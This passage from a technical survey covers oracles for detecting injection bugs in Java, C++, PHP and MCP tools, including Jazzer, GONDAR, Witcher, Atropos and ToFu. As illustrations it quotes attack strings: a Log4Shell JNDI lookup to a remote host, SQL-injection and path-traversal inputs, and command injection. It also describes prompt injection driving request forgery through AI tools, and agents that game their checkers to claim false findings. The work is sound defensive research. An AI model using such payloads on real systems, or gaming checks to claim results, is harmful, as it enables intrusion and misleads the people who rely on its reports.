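According to Team Atlanta, these additions came after Code Intelligence had stopped maintaining the open-source version of Jazzer as AIxCC began and then reversed the decision. Developers can also write their own hooks, so a team with an unusual sink doesn't have to wait for a new release.

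Some injections, such as cross-site scripting, have no sink inside the JVM, but Meumertzheim shows how an assertion can detect one. JsonSanitizer is a Java library that makes JSON safe to embed in a web page, so its output must never contain a closing script tag. A harness asserted this, and the fuzzer found an input that violated the assertion, a bug that became CVE-2021-23899.

### Log4Shell and the lookup detector

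The detector for JNDI lookups exists because of Log4Shell, a vulnerability in Log4j, a logging library that many Java programs use. JNDI is Java's interface for finding objects by name, including objects on other servers. If an attacker sent text such as `${jndi:ldap://example.com/a}` and the program logged it, Log4j would contact that server and look up the object. On some versions of Java, the server's response could make the JVM run the attacker's code.

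The Log4j flaw became public on 9 December 2021, and attacks began soon afterwards. A fuzzer could have run the faulty code earlier without detecting the flaw, because Log4j was using a feature its developers had built deliberately.

Meumertzheim's *Finding the log4j RCE With Fuzzing* describes how Code Intelligence added a detector for remote lookups to its commercial product and then released it in Jazzer. Google (2021) awarded the company $25,000 for the work, and the two companies began fuzzing Log4j continuously through OSS-Fuzz.

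The small harness that reproduces Log4Shell turns the fuzzer's bytes into a string and logs it as an error. In the run that Meumertzheim showed in 2022, Jazzer found the vulnerability in 284 seconds. The input was mostly junk but contained `${jndi:ldap://g.co/`. The fuzzer's log shows that Jazzer had inserted `ldap://g.co/` from its table of useful values, so the detector's guidance had supplied the part of the attack that names a server.

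The guidance also had to help the fuzzer discover the word `jndi`, which Log4j uses as a key to look up the right handler in a map. To make this possible, Jazzer's developers had to improve its tracking of map lookups.

Meumertzheim cautioned that "hindsight is 20/20" and that Jazzer finds the flaw only when it fuzzes Log4j itself. A company fuzzing its own application would probably have missed the bug in the library. The larger problem is that Jazzer gained its detector for JNDI lookups only after attackers were exploiting one. Somebody has to write a detector before it can catch similar mistakes in other projects.

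### SystemSan and native code

Google also applied the idea outside Java with SystemSan, which looks for bugs that let an attacker run arbitrary commands. It uses `ptrace`, a Linux mechanism that lets one process observe another's requests to the operating system. Programs make the same kind of request to start a command whether they are written in C++, Python or another language, so one detector can watch them all.

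Google's *Fuzzing beyond memory corruption* (2022) describes a bug that SystemSan caught in TinyGLTF, a C++ library for reading 3D models. TinyGLTF passed the image paths listed in a model file to `wordexp`, a standard function that expands a path as a shell would, including running any command between backticks.

Google demonstrated the flaw with a model whose image path was the letter *a* followed by a command in backticks. When a program loaded the model, the command wrote a word to a new file. TinyGLTF's memory stayed intact, so ASan could not detect the flaw. The library's developers soon fixed the bug (CVE-2022-3008).

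SystemSan monitors the operating system, so it can observe a new process or an opened file. But a Java program can load a dangerous class or query a database in its own memory without making a distinctive system call. Jazzer's hooks cover these cases because they intercept the method call, where the arguments still have a clear meaning.

In 2022 Google had prototypes for JavaScript and Python libraries, and an outside contributor had added detection of arbitrary file access. Google also offered $11,337 to anyone who integrated a new detector that found at least two new vulnerabilities in OSS-Fuzz projects. SystemSan's later history is unclear, and the TinyGLTF bug is the only specific bug that Google's announcement credits to it.

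### What Jazzer has found

*Jazzer* (Toffalini, Holz and colleagues, 2026) reports that OSS-Fuzz used the fuzzer on 205 open-source Java projects over three years, finding 1,217 security issues that were confirmed and fixed. In the paper's comparison on eleven libraries, Jazzer ran faster and covered more code than JQF, an earlier Java fuzzer, and found 18 bugs that earlier work had missed.

The figure of 1,217 shows that fuzzing Java is worthwhile, but not that the injection detectors were responsible for the findings. It combines all types of security issue, without separate counts for injection or for exceptions and timeouts. Meumertzheim's talk lists infinite loops and exhausted memory among the usual security problems in Java, and a fuzzer can find both without checking any sink.

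The findings that Code Intelligence lists publicly are similarly mixed. One is a flaw in the database hsqldb that let an attacker run code through values in a prepared statement (CVE-2022-41853). Others include a bug that made small protobuf messages use minutes of processor time and two image files that made Java's own libraries run out of memory. Google wrote in 2022 that the newer Java detectors, such as those for deserialization and LDAP injection, had already found vulnerabilities that were awaiting disclosure, but it did not say how many.

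Injection bugs were probably a minority of the 1,217 issues. Java programs can exhaust memory or throw an unexpected exception in many ways, and a fuzzer can detect these failures without a sentinel. To report an injection, it needs an input that reaches one of a limited set of sinks and also meets the condition set by that sink's detector.

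## How many Java injection bugs the detectors catch

Toffalini and colleagues count 1,217 issues that Jazzer found. Estimating how many it missed requires a set of known bugs. Fleischer and colleagues assembled one to test GONDAR, a tool they built that adds language-model agents to Jazzer. They measured separately how often a search reaches a sink and how often it then makes the detector report a bug.

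### A benchmark of 54 known bugs

Five security researchers spent 15 person-weeks collecting 54 vulnerabilities in 22 open-source Java projects. The bugs cover 12 CWE types, including path traversal, command injection, unsafe deserialization and server-side request forgery. The researchers wrote harnesses for 19 published vulnerabilities, took 20 from AIxCC rounds before the final, and planted the other 15. Jenkins and the document library Tika together contain 24 of the 54.

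The benchmark includes only bugs that a dynamic detector can confirm, and each comes with a working exploit and a harness that reaches the bug. Given the right input, the detectors should therefore report all 54. The experiments test how well different tools search for that input. The results can't be used to estimate what share of real injection flaws the detectors would recognise, and they don't apply to other silent classes, such as authorization bypasses and timing leaks.

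Fleischer and colleagues first gave Jazzer far more computing power than most projects have available. They ran each of the 53 harnesses on 50 processor cores for 24 hours, a total of more than seven core-years.

| Outcome for Jazzer | Bugs | Share |
|---|---|---|
| Never reached the sink | 25 | 46% |
| Reached the sink but did not trigger the detector | 21 | 39% |
| Triggered the detector | 8 | 15% |

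Most of that computing power added little. A run with three cores for 12 hours, about a thirty-third of the computing power, reached 26 sinks instead of 29 and triggered the same number of bugs, eight. On half the targets, Jazzer reached 95% of its final code coverage within 15 minutes.

### Why reaching the sink was not enough

The 21 bugs in the middle row are the most informative about the detectors, because Jazzer had already run the dangerous call. Fleischer and colleagues found three causes:

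- In 18 cases, triggering the bug took an input with a particular format, several interacting calls or some other intricate condition. One example is an XML document that has to satisfy the program's type rules before the program will rebuild an object from it.
- In two cases, the detector's condition needed a longer sequence of bytes than Jazzer's feedback on comparisons could guide it to.
- In one case, the program used a call that Jazzer's feedback did not cover, so the fuzzer had nothing to steer by.

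Random changes also tend to undo the fuzzer's progress. For example, if an input is a valid ZIP archive containing a file name, changing the name can corrupt the archive, and the program then rejects the input before it reaches the sink.

Fuzzers did better in an earlier experiment by Team Atlanta. *ATLANTIS*, the team's report, describes a test on 42 bugs in which each harness had more than 100 cores for eight hours. The fuzzers triggered 15 of the bugs, reached 16 others without triggering them and never reached 11. They therefore triggered 36% of the bugs, compared with 15% in the GONDAR study, so the rate depends heavily on which bugs a benchmark contains. Intricate conditions were again the main obstacle, blocking nine of the 16 bugs that were reached but not triggered. In four others, the fuzzer produced so many inputs reaching the sink that it did not prioritize the useful ones.

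Team Atlanta then gave a language model the inputs that had reached the 16 sinks, along with the surrounding code. The model triggered 13 of the bugs, six of them with a single query to o1-preview, an OpenAI model from 2024. This work led to GONDAR.

### How GONDAR reaches and triggers sinks

GONDAR first lists the calls worth attacking, using the catalogue of sinks from CodeQL, GitHub's tool for searching source code. CodeQL found 8,262 candidate calls in the 22 projects. GONDAR discards calls with constant arguments, calls in test code and calls that the harness apparently can't reach. A language model then removes calls that the surrounding code makes safe. With OpenAI's GPT-5, 383 candidates remained, including 52 of the 54 real bugs.

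An exploration agent tries to reach each remaining sink:

1. GONDAR picks one chain of function calls leading from the harness to the sink. It prefers chains along which input appears to flow, and then shorter ones.
2. The agent reads the code of each function in the chain and writes a Python script that builds an input.
3. A debugger runs the program on that input, with a breakpoint at the sink.
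4. If the run misses the sink, the debugger reports how far along the chain it got, and the agent revises the script.

Jazzer runs at the same time and adds the agent's inputs to its own pool. When an input from the agent or Jazzer reaches a sink, GONDAR can pass it to an exploitation agent. This agent also receives the call stack, the vulnerability type and the condition that Jazzer's detector checks. It writes a script to meet the condition, runs the result, reads the log and tries again.

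After these attempts, Jazzer spends five minutes altering the agent's inputs. It ignores code coverage, because the sink is already within reach, and tracks only its progress on comparisons. This often fixes an input that was nearly right. Depending on the model, fuzzing succeeded in 17% to 43% of the cases where the agent had failed.

GONDAR's final output includes only inputs that triggered a Jazzer detector. This check matters because only about 14% of GONDAR's 383 candidates were real bugs. Reviewers of the paper raised this as a concern, and Fleischer and colleagues reply that a wrong candidate costs money for model calls but never becomes a false report. They also note that established code scanners did worse on the same projects. CodeQL's own security queries flagged 14 of the 54 bugs and 215 harmless calls, while SpotBugs, another widely used scanner, flagged 20 bugs and 244 harmless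 calls.

### Results and cost

| Configuration | Bugs triggered, of 54 | Cost |
|---|---|---|
| Jazzer, 3 cores for 12 hours | 8 | $98 |
| Jazzer, 50 cores for 24 hours | 8 | $3,264 |
| Directed Jazzer | 12 | $98 |
| Simple agent with Gemini 2.5 Pro | 16 | $117 |
| GONDAR with GPT-5-nano | 27 | $182 |
| GONDAR with GLM-5 | 35 | $392 |
| GONDAR with GPT-5 | 37 | $2,429 |
| GONDAR with Gemini 2.5 Pro | 41 | $3,051 |

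The cost figures cover the whole benchmark. Directed Jazzer favours inputs that come closer to a chosen place in the code, and the experimenters gave it the true locations of the bugs. The simple agent also received each bug's location and type, and it could read the source code and run the harness. GONDAR had to find the locations itself and still triggered more than twice as many bugs as either.

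Fleischer and colleagues conclude that GONDAR leads because of how it divides the problem, not because of the underlying model's ability. The comparison with the simple agent only partly supports this, because the simple agent might have done better with a larger budget. GONDAR's best run cost about $2,950 in model calls, while the simple agent's cost less than $19. However, much of GONDAR's money went on candidates that were not bugs, which the simple agent never had to consider.

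GONDAR costs less than the $3,264 large-scale fuzzing run, but the $98 run triggered just as many bugs as that one. For a project with little money, the more useful comparison is between plain Jazzer at $98 and GONDAR with GLM-5, an open-weight Chinese model, at $392. The extra $294 bought 27 more bugs. Moving from GLM-5 to Gemini 2.5 Pro bought another six at about $443 each.

Reaching sinks was the expensive part. With Gemini 2.5 Pro, exploration accounted for 83% of the bill and exploitation for about 10%.

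With GPT-5, the complete system reached 42 sinks and triggered 37 bugs. Removing the exploration agent cut the sinks reached to 29, and removing the exploitation agent cut the bugs triggered to 18. That is still ten more bugs than Jazzer triggered alone, because better inputs also help the fuzzer. Seven bugs appeared only when the agents and fuzzer worked together. Typically, the agent produced an input close to the right one, and the fuzzer's rapid mutation turned it into one that triggered the bug.

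The complete GONDAR system reached ten path-traversal sinks and triggered the bugs at eight of them. Without the exploitation agent, it triggered two. Many of the others required a valid ZIP archive or Java class file, which Jazzer kept breaking. Without the exploration agent, GONDAR reached five sinks and triggered the bugs at all five.

Some of the language models may have seen published bugs during training. This probably explains little of the result, because 32 of the 54 bugs had never been public and only one had a public exploit that might resemble the answer. An early version also worked on unfamiliar code in the AIxCC final, where it triggered seven planted bugs and found three previously unknown vulnerabilities.

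### The eleven bugs that remained

No configuration of GONDAR triggered the last 11 bugs, mainly because they all required complicated input. Four needed unusual modifications to a common file format. Three needed a complex format and several interactions in the right order. Two needed input that mixed formats, such as an image embedded in an HTML page, and two needed elaborate serialized Java objects.

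These are failures of search, since a detector would have reported each bug given the right input. The strongest models in the experiment date from 2025, and the stronger models released since then could probably find some of the 11.

Fleischer and colleagues examined 182 failed exploitation attempts by two models and attributed 122 to complex formats and 60 to unmet detector conditions. Deserialization accounted for 22 of these 60 and XPath injection for 15. Command injection was the most expensive type for GPT-5 because the model had to keep refining commands to satisfy Jazzer, which an attacker would not have to do.

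### Planted bugs in C and Java

The AIxCC final allows a comparison between Java and C. Zhang and colleagues reran ordinary fuzzing, without any language model, on the 63 vulnerabilities planted for the final. They gave each harness 16 cores for up to six hours, ran the experiment three times and counted a bug as found if any run triggered it.

| | C | Java |
|---|---|---|
| Planted bugs | 40 | 23 |
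| Triggered by parallel fuzzing | 30 (75%) | 4 (17%) |
| Further bugs triggered by contest systems | 8 | 14 |
| Triggered by either | 38 (95%) | 18 (78%) |

Zhang and colleagues give three reasons for the low rate in Java. The inputs must satisfy more complex rules, such as those of XML. Many of the Java bugs are timeouts or exhausted memory, which fuzzers handle badly. OSS-Fuzz also supplies lower-quality sample inputs for Java projects than for C projects.

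The C figure is somewhat inflated. Of the 40 C bugs, 21 came from Wireshark, shadowsocks and systemd, and the organisers deliberately made most of these easy to find to test how well systems repaired bugs and recognised duplicates. Even if fuzzing triggered all 21, it also triggered nine of the other 19 (47%), which is still well above the rate in Java.

The Java figure includes bugs that aren't injections, so it is not a success rate for injection detectors. At least nine of the 23 Java bugs were endless loops, exhausted memory, a slow regular expression or a crash of the JVM. The AI Cyber Challenge's notes on one challenge built on the poi library list backdoors, excessive resource use and a "zip slip", a path traversal in which a file name inside an archive points outside the folder where the program unpacks it. Of these, only the zip slip is clearly the kind of bug an injection detector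 looks for.

The contest systems' 22 additional bugs suggest that language models helped, as in the GONDAR study. Three teams used little more than basic fuzzing and language models, and each triggered several bugs that fuzzing had missed. The Java examples include inputs that had to pass through URL encoding, Unicode normalisation or compression before they reached the faulty code. A fuzzer gets little feedback on its progress through such steps, but a language model can read the code and work backwards to a suitable input.

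But 15 of the 22 were in challenges where the systems received a recent code change and had to find the bug it introduced, so they had much less code to examine than in a search of a whole project. Two teams also used directed fuzzing without language models, but it found no bugs in these challenges that other teams missed. This agrees with the small gain from directed Jazzer.

Researchers from Team Atlanta led both this analysis and the GONDAR study, so the two are not fully independent. But they cover different bugs, because GONDAR's benchmark includes none from the final. In both, plain fuzzing triggered less than a fifth of the known Java bugs, and language models triggered most of the rest when a detector existed.

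### What a better search cannot fix

A better search helps only if the program can meet a detector's condition. Neither study measures how many injection flaws cannot meet such a condition, because both used bugs that an oracle could confirm. A flaw can be unable to meet one for four reasons.

Jazzer sometimes has a suitable detector but no hook to guide the fuzzer towards it. An agent that knows the detector's condition can then supply the sentinel without that guidance. GONDAR triggered four bugs where missing instrumentation had hindered Jazzer. *ATLANTIS* reports significant gaps between the calls that can be dangerous and those that Jazzer monitors. Team Atlanta extended its list of targets beyond the calls that Jazzer hooks. For example, it added the class that represents a web address, because code that uses this class may then open a connection, which Jazzer does check.

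If Jazzer has no hook at a call or anywhere in the code it leads to, an agent can deliver a working attack there and Jazzer will treat the run as normal. Adding the call to a list of targets does not change this. Jazzer had no hook for JNDI lookups until Log4Shell prompted Code Intelligence to add one.

An attacker with **partial control** of a value may control enough of it to do harm but not enough to produce the sentinel. Suppose a program lets users choose a conversion tool by name and runs the matching file in `/opt/tools/`. A user who enters `../../bin/sh` makes it run `/opt/tools/../../bin/sh`, which is the system shell. The path always begins with `/opt/tools/`, so it can never equal the sentinel `jazze`, and the command detector reports nothing for any input.

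The web page that runs `ping` has the same problem, since the attacker controls only an argument. To catch such bugs, the detector needs a different condition, such as one that examines how the shell would interpret the argument. More fuzzing or a better agent will not make the existing condition detect them.

A program may store an attacker's text safely and misuse it later. For example, a website might save a user's chosen name correctly, then paste it into a new database query when it builds a monthly report. If the harness covers only registration, that query never runs during the test. Testing the report separately may not help either, because a tester would normally fill the database with harmless names.

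If one input can make the program perform several actions in a row, an agent can search for a sequence that triggers the bug. GONDAR triggered three bugs that required more than one interaction. An agent can't do this when the second action happens in another program or after the harness has finished. Those cases would require a harness that covers both actions and uses the same database for them.

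A detector can't report on code that never runs, so GONDAR needs a harness that leads to the function containing the sink, and it will miss vulnerabilities in any code the harness leaves out. The benchmark is more favourable than ordinary use in this respect. For the 19 published vulnerabilities, the researchers wrote harnesses after they knew where the bugs were, which a developer looking for unknown bugs can't do.

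The same limit affected AIxCC. The final included five projects without harnesses, among them OpenSSL, and the organisers did not score them. Zhang and colleagues list automatic harness generation as a task for future contests. Tools that write harnesses already exist, and Fleischer and colleagues expect GONDAR to benefit from them.

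## Detecting injection in web applications

A web application runs continuously, answers requests over a network and usually keeps its data in a database. Most research on fuzzing such applications concerns PHP, a language used by about three quarters of websites.

An HTTP request carries named values such as `page=login`, and a fuzzer is unlikely to guess the names. *Atropos* (Güler, Schumilo et al., 2024) describes a PHP fuzzer that learns them from the running program. Suppose Atropos sends `abc=xyz`. The modified PHP interpreter reports that the application looked for a value called `page`, so the fuzzer tries `page=xyz`. The interpreter then reports that the application compared `xyz` with `login`, and the fuzzer tries `page=login`. On one test application, Atropos found 24 bugs with this kind of feedback and none without it.

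Web applications keep state between requests, so one request can log the user out or delete a record that the next request needs. Atropos therefore runs the application, its database and its files in a virtual machine, and restores a snapshot after each input. A single input may contain several requests, so Atropos can still catch some stored injections. It found one in which one page saved a value and another pasted it into an SQL query.

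Injection causes harm outside the web application itself, which may be in a database, a visitor's browser or another server. Even a real crash can go unnoticed. *What All the Phuzz Is About* (Neef, Kleissner and Seifert, 2024) points out that when the PHP interpreter crashes, the web server still returns a valid response with an error code. Applications can also catch database errors and show an ordinary page.

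### Turning syntax errors into crashes

Witcher, which Trickel, Pagani and colleagues (2023) present in *Toss a Fault to Your Witcher*, converts an injection into the signal that fuzzers already understand:

1. The fuzzer sends a request containing `id=1'`.
2. The application pastes the value into an SQL query and sends the query to the database.
3. The stray quotation mark makes the query invalid, and the database replies with a syntax error.
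4. Witcher has hooked `recv`, the standard function that receives the reply. When it sees the error message, it triggers a segmentation fault, the signal that normally follows an illegal memory access.
5. The fuzzer records a crash and saves the request.

For command injection, Trickel and colleagues changed three lines of dash, a small shell that many Linux systems use, so that a command with broken syntax causes the same fault. Unlike Jazzer's command detector, this change covers the web page that runs `ping`, because an unmatched quotation mark in the address breaks the command's syntax.

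Both checks are outside the application's code, so Witcher could test programs written in PHP, Python, Node.js, Java, Ruby and C. In 18 applications, it found 23 of 36 known vulnerabilities and 67 new ones. But 43 of the new ones were in a single hospital management system, and Witcher found nothing in current versions of popular applications such as phpBB.

Trickel and colleagues attribute none of the 13 misses to the oracle. In eight cases, the crawler that collects pages for testing never found the right address. The oracle explains much of Witcher's lead over Burp, a commercial scanner that detects vulnerabilities from an application's responses. On nine PHP applications, Witcher found 70 vulnerabilities, while Burp found 18 even when it started from the requests Witcher's crawler had collected.

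### What a syntax error proves

Two versions of a page look up a user by number. Page A uses the input unchanged, and page B first deletes everything except digits.

```php
$id = $_GET['id'];                                // page A
$id = preg_replace('/[^0-9]/', '', $_GET['id']);  // page B

$query = "SELECT name FROM users WHERE id = " . $id;
```

| Page | Input | End of the query | Database's response | Witcher's verdict | Truth |
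|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| A | `7` | `id = 7` | One name | No report | Normal use |
| A | `7'` | `id = 7'` | Syntax error | Report | The page is vulnerable |
| A | `7 OR 1=1` | `id = 7 OR 1=1` | Every name | No report | A working attack |
| B | `x` | `id = ` | Syntax error | Report | A harmless bug |

On page B, the letter `x` disappears, leaving an incomplete query that fails. An attacker gains nothing from this because only digits can reach the database.

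Witcher misses `7 OR 1=1` on page A because the query stays valid, just as Jazzer misses `' OR '1'='1`. The fuzzer will almost certainly also try something like `7'`, which makes the query invalid, so Witcher still finds the flaw. Besides 90 vulnerabilities, Witcher reported two false positives and three bugs that Trickel and colleagues did not count as exploitable.

The method fails when an application lets only well-formed input reach the query. Simanjuntak and Csallner (2026) argue in *ZIMPAF & RedPhuzz* that this leaves real flaws undetected because no input causes an error.

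### Hooks inside PHP

Atropos looks for errors inside the PHP interpreter, so it can detect them even when the application shows an ordinary page. Most of its oracles also require the suspicious call to contain text from the fuzzer's input. Atropos would probably not report page B, because the page deletes the letters of the marker text that Atropos looks for in the query.

| Vulnerability | Condition for a report in Atropos |
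|---|---|
| SQL injection | A query containing the fuzzer's text has a syntax error |
| PHP code injection | Code containing the fuzzer's text has a syntax error, or PHP code from the fuzzer runs |
| Command injection | The application tries to run a program that doesn't exist, or runs a planted one |
| File inclusion | The application tries to load code from a missing file whose path contains the fuzzer's text, or loads a planted file |
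| Object injection | PHP fails to rebuild an object from the fuzzer's text |
| Server-side request forgery | The application contacts a private network address, and the request contains the fuzzer's text |
| File access | The application reads, writes, renames or deletes a PHP file whose name contains the fuzzer's text, or does so to a planted file |
| File upload | The application accepts a PHP file |

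Güler and colleagues tested Atropos on three deliberately vulnerable applications with 52 relevant bugs. In 24 hours, it found 39 bugs on one processor core and 49 on 40 cores, with no false alarms. The static code checker that found the most bugs detected 37 and raised 59 false alarms.

In 56 real applications, Atropos found seven new vulnerabilities and reported three false positives. Two of the false positives were features that intentionally let administrators run any SQL query or upload any file. The third was a query that was broken for reasons unrelated to unsafe input.

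The last two conditions in the table are narrow. Wang and colleagues object that an attacker can upload a different dangerous type of file, and that the application may save uploads through a function Atropos doesn't monitor. Güler and colleagues chose the narrow rule because many applications accept files for legitimate reasons.

Neef and colleagues' fuzzer, PHUZZ, hooks PHP functions through an extension, without modifying the interpreter. It found 86 of 87 known vulnerabilities (99%), while Burp found 75%. Most of the gap came from flaws that act on the server, of which PHUZZ found 98% and Burp 58%. Of the flaws visible in the returned page, PHUZZ found 100% and Burp 95%. These rates mainly measure detection, because the experimenters gave every tool the address of each vulnerable page and disabled login checks where necessary.

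RedPhuzz, Simanjuntak and Csallner's successor to PHUZZ, addresses attacks that leave the query valid. It checks whether part of the input has become SQL logic in the query, and then whether the database call succeeded. It could therefore report `7 OR 1=1` on page A. RedPhuzz also recognises safe patterns, such as prepared statements, which send the query and the user's value to the database separately. On 86 test cases it found every vulnerability, while PHUZZ missed 16. These cases came from known benchmarks, so the result doesn't establish how many flaws RedPhuzz would miss in unfamiliar applications.

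### Planted targets and callbacks

An oracle can also detect successful attacks. Atropos, for example, checks whether an injected command runs its planted program. This approach suits AI agents better than relying on syntax errors.

*Taint-Style Vulnerability Detection and Confirmation for Node.js Packages Using LLM Agent Reasoning* (2026) describes LLMVD.js, an agent whose exploits must pass a test for each type of flaw, regardless of the agent's own judgment. A code injection exploit must call a marker function, and a path traversal exploit must read and print a prepared file. Before each attempt, the system deletes any traces of earlier command injections so that an old success can't count as a new one.

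Unlike all these checks, a **callback** does not require access to the machine that runs the application. The tester sends a payload that makes the application connect to a server the tester controls, then waits for the connection. Trickel and colleagues write that SRFuzzer, a tool for testing the web pages of home routers, detects command injection this way. If each payload contains a unique address, the tester can match a late connection to the request that caused it, which helps with stored injection.

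Detecting injection through callbacks requires the injected command to be valid, whereas Witcher can detect injection from a malformed one. A firewall that blocks outgoing traffic will also hide a successful attack. A callback does not by itself prove server-side request forgery, because some applications, such as those that show link previews, are supposed to contact addresses that users supply. The tester therefore needs a policy on which destinations are forbidden.

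### Checking whether injected script ran

Trickel and colleagues left cross-site scripting out of Witcher because browsers tolerate malformed HTML, so there is often no syntax error to detect. PHUZZ adds a marker to its input and searches for it in the structure of the returned page. This takes little computation, but a page can contain an attacker's text without executing it.

A stronger oracle opens the page in a real browser and reports whether the script ran. That was enough for older scanners, but *RECEIPT* (Lyu, Shieh and colleagues, 2026) shows that it fails with capable AI agents. With only this check, the agent in the study claimed 111 vulnerabilities, of which 10 were real. In some false claims, the agent had written the script directly into the database or run it in the checker's browser tab. In others, it had used an administrator account that was allowed to add scripts.

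RECEIPT, their replacement, separates the attacker from the victim:

1. It restores a clean copy of the application, which discards anything the agent changed while exploring.
2. It runs the agent's attack script, which can only send HTTP requests and has only the attacker's login details.
3. It opens a browser as the victim and performs ordinary actions from a fixed list.
4. It accepts the finding only if the attacker's script executes in the victim's browser.

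These roles form a small policy that someone has to set for each application. In 50 applications with no vulnerabilities known to the researchers, the agent and RECEIPT together found 30 vulnerabilities, 24 of them new, for $20 per application. Lyu and colleagues found no false positives. In 45 other applications with a known cross-site scripting flaw, the system found that flaw in only 36% of them, so a report is far more reliable than a clean result.

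### Tools that language models call

A language-model agent acts through tools, which are functions that search files, fetch web pages or run commands. The model chooses a tool and writes its arguments, often after reading untrusted text, so an attacker who influences that text can reach the same sinks as in an ordinary web application. *From Prompt Injection to Web Exploitation* (2026) tested server-side request forgery through seven models and found that most carried out the direct attacks, while others consistently refused. Because refusal depends on the model, it is not evidence that the tool is safe.

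*ToFu* (Ananto, Prevost-Avenel and colleagues, 2026) tests servers that offer tools through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common standard for connecting tools to agents. It sends hostile arguments directly to each tool, without going through a model. It treats the tool's description, which is written to help a model use the tool, as a rough policy. For instance, a tool whose description says it reads files "within the workspace" should not open a file anywhere else.

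A language model reads the description and selects from 74 prepared checks, which then work in two ways:

- **Watching what the tool does.** In Python tools, hooks record operations such as opening a file or a network connection. If a tool opens `../../etc/passwd`, the check resolves the full path and reports that it lies outside the workspace.
- **Testing whether the tool rejected the input.** Some tools don't allow hooks, so ToFu looks at the response.

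For the second kind, let *x* be the input and *T*(*x*) the tool's response, and let *E* be any side effects that ToFu observed. *V*(*x*) means that the check regards *x* as malicious. ToFu reports a violation if

*V*(*x*) ∧ ¬Reject(*T*(*x*), *E*).

Before the test, the language model specifies what counts as a rejection for each tool. Some tools must return an error, while others may return a harmless value such as an empty list. The check is turned off for tools that are meant to accept such input. During the test, fixed code applies these rules without using the model.

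This second check covers more tools but gives weaker evidence. A tool that silently removes `../` from a path and opens a permitted file does no harm, but its normal response can look like a failure to reject the attack.

Ananto and colleagues ran ToFu on 273 servers, generally for 60 seconds per tool, with longer runs on 34 of them.

| Stage | Count |
|---|---|
| Candidate bugs | 508 |
| Rejected by hand as not vulnerable | 103 |
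| Duplicates | 152 |
| Verified bugs | 253, in 118 servers |

About a fifth of the candidates were therefore false, so ToFu's reports need human review. The verified bugs include 64 path traversals, seven server-side request forgeries and three command injections. Another 173, more than two thirds of the total, are milder. In 115 of these, the tool returns hostile text without making it safe for a web page, and in the other 58 an attacker can forge log entries. How much harm these do depends on what later displays the text or reads the log. None of the 253 bugs needed a crash to be detected, though some had visible effects, such as a server deleting files outside its workspace on the test machine.

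ToFu's results depend heavily on which checks its model selects for each tool. When Ananto and colleagues switched on all 74 checks for every tool, over 90% of the reports on newly flagged tools were false. When they removed the model's selection and kept only the checks that always run, path traversal findings fell from about 100 to none. For one JavaScript server, the model mistakenly chose a check that works only in Python, and ToFu missed five request forgeries.

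VIPER-MCP, a rival system in which an agent tries to exploit suspected flaws, confirmed 11 exploits on the same servers. Four were on servers where ToFu reported nothing, and all four involved tools meant to run code or commands from the caller. Whether these count as vulnerabilities depends on who should be allowed to call the tool.

ToFu misses real bugs, often because it can't run the code. Of the servers that only other tools flagged, about 63% failed to start, hung, or rejected every input before reaching their main logic, for example because ToFu had no valid login. ToFu also tests one call at a time, so it will generally miss an attack that one call stores and a later call triggers.

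## Fuzz harnesses that trigger a detector without a vulnerability

An injection detector tests what arrives at a sink, not whether an attacker could have sent it there. A contrived harness is one that makes a detector fire by using the code in a way no attacker could bring about. Let *F* be the set of values that the harness can deliver to a sink, and *A* the set that an attacker can deliver to the same sink in the real program. Jazzer's command detector can fire when

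`jazze` ∈ *F*,

but the program is vulnerable only if *A* contains something harmful. With a contrived harness, *F* contains the sentinel and *A* contains nothing harmful. The detector has no information about *A*, because it runs only with the harness.

### Three contrived harnesses

Suppose an image-conversion server is written in Java and attackers can access it only by sending web requests. Jazzer would report a bug with each of the following harnesses, although the server is safe.

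**A direct command call.** Jazzer calls this function with each input it generates:

```java
static void fuzzerTestOneInput(byte[] data) throws IOException {
    new ProcessBuilder(new String(data)).start();
}
```

Jazzer reports command injection when the input bytes spell `jazze`. Reading the harness shows that it does run commands from its input but never calls the server's code.

**Skipped validation.** The server starts its conversion tools like this:

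```java
public void convert(String tool, String file) throws IOException {
    if (!Set.of("png2jpg", "png2gif").contains(tool))
        throw new IllegalArgumentException();
    run(tool, file);
}

void run(String tool, String file) throws IOException {
    new ProcessBuilder(tool, file).start();
}
```

Every web request goes through `convert`, which accepts only two tool names. The harness skips `convert` and calls the internal function `run` with the fuzzer's text as the tool name. The stack trace includes the server's own code, so a reviewer has to find every caller of `run` to learn that no request can pass `jazze` to it.

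*FalseCrashReducer* (Amusuo, Liu et al., 2025) describes a real case in C++. `GetRoot`, a function for the FlexBuffers data format, reads the last two bytes of a buffer without checking that the buffer is long enough. A machine-written harness gave it a one-byte buffer, and ASan reported an overflow. The project's command-line tool, `flatc`, first calls a function that rejects any buffer shorter than three bytes, so a malformed file can't cause this crash there. A program that skipped that check on untrusted data would still be exposed.

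**Trusted code.** The server's administrator can write scripts that rename converted files. A public method, `evaluate`, runs them, and its documentation states that scripts must come from the administrator. The harness passes the fuzzer's text to `evaluate`, and Jazzer reports script injection when the text contains the detector's sentinel.

This harness calls a public method correctly and bypasses no check. Its only fault is treating the script as attacker-controlled, which contradicts the documentation but not the code. If any visitor could submit a script through a web form on the server, the same harness would demonstrate a serious vulnerability.

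### Honest mistakes and real disputes

A harness can also cause a false report when its author tries to use the code properly but gets a detail wrong. *FuzzAgent* (Lyu, Chen and colleagues, 2026) gives an example from libaom, an AV1 video library. A machine-written harness uses one bit of the input to choose between two image formats, I420 and I444. I420 stores each of its two colour planes at a quarter of the image's full size, while I444 stores them at full size. The harness always allocates memory for I420, even when the input selects I444.

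For an I444 image of 64 by 64 pixels, the harness allocates 1,024 bytes per colour plane, but the encoder needs 4,096, so it reads past the end of the allocation. ASan's report shows six library functions between the harness and the bad read, which makes the crash look like a fault deep inside libaom. PromeFuzz, a system that writes harnesses and sorts the resulting crashes with a language model, classified the crash as a library bug.

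An agent trying to get credit and one that misread the documentation could write the same line of code, so the code alone may not show whether the misuse was deliberate or a mistake. The difference matters because a mistaken harness is often worth repairing. In *Quality-Assured Fuzz Harness Generation via the Four Principles Framework* (2026), Sheng, Chen and colleagues corrected the order of calls in an OpenSSL harness, and the repaired harness exposed an out-of-bounds read that had been in OpenSSL's code for the old DES cipher for more than 25 years.

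In other cases, people agree on what the program does but not on whether it is a flaw. FuzzAgent reports six findings that were dropped after maintainers responded. Three were expected behaviour under unwritten rules. One of these was a report that the video library libvpx ran out of memory, which its maintainers closed because the format permits images of 65,536 by 65,536 pixels. Two others were failures that the maintainers had ruled out of scope for the current release. Only the sixth was a mistake in the harness.

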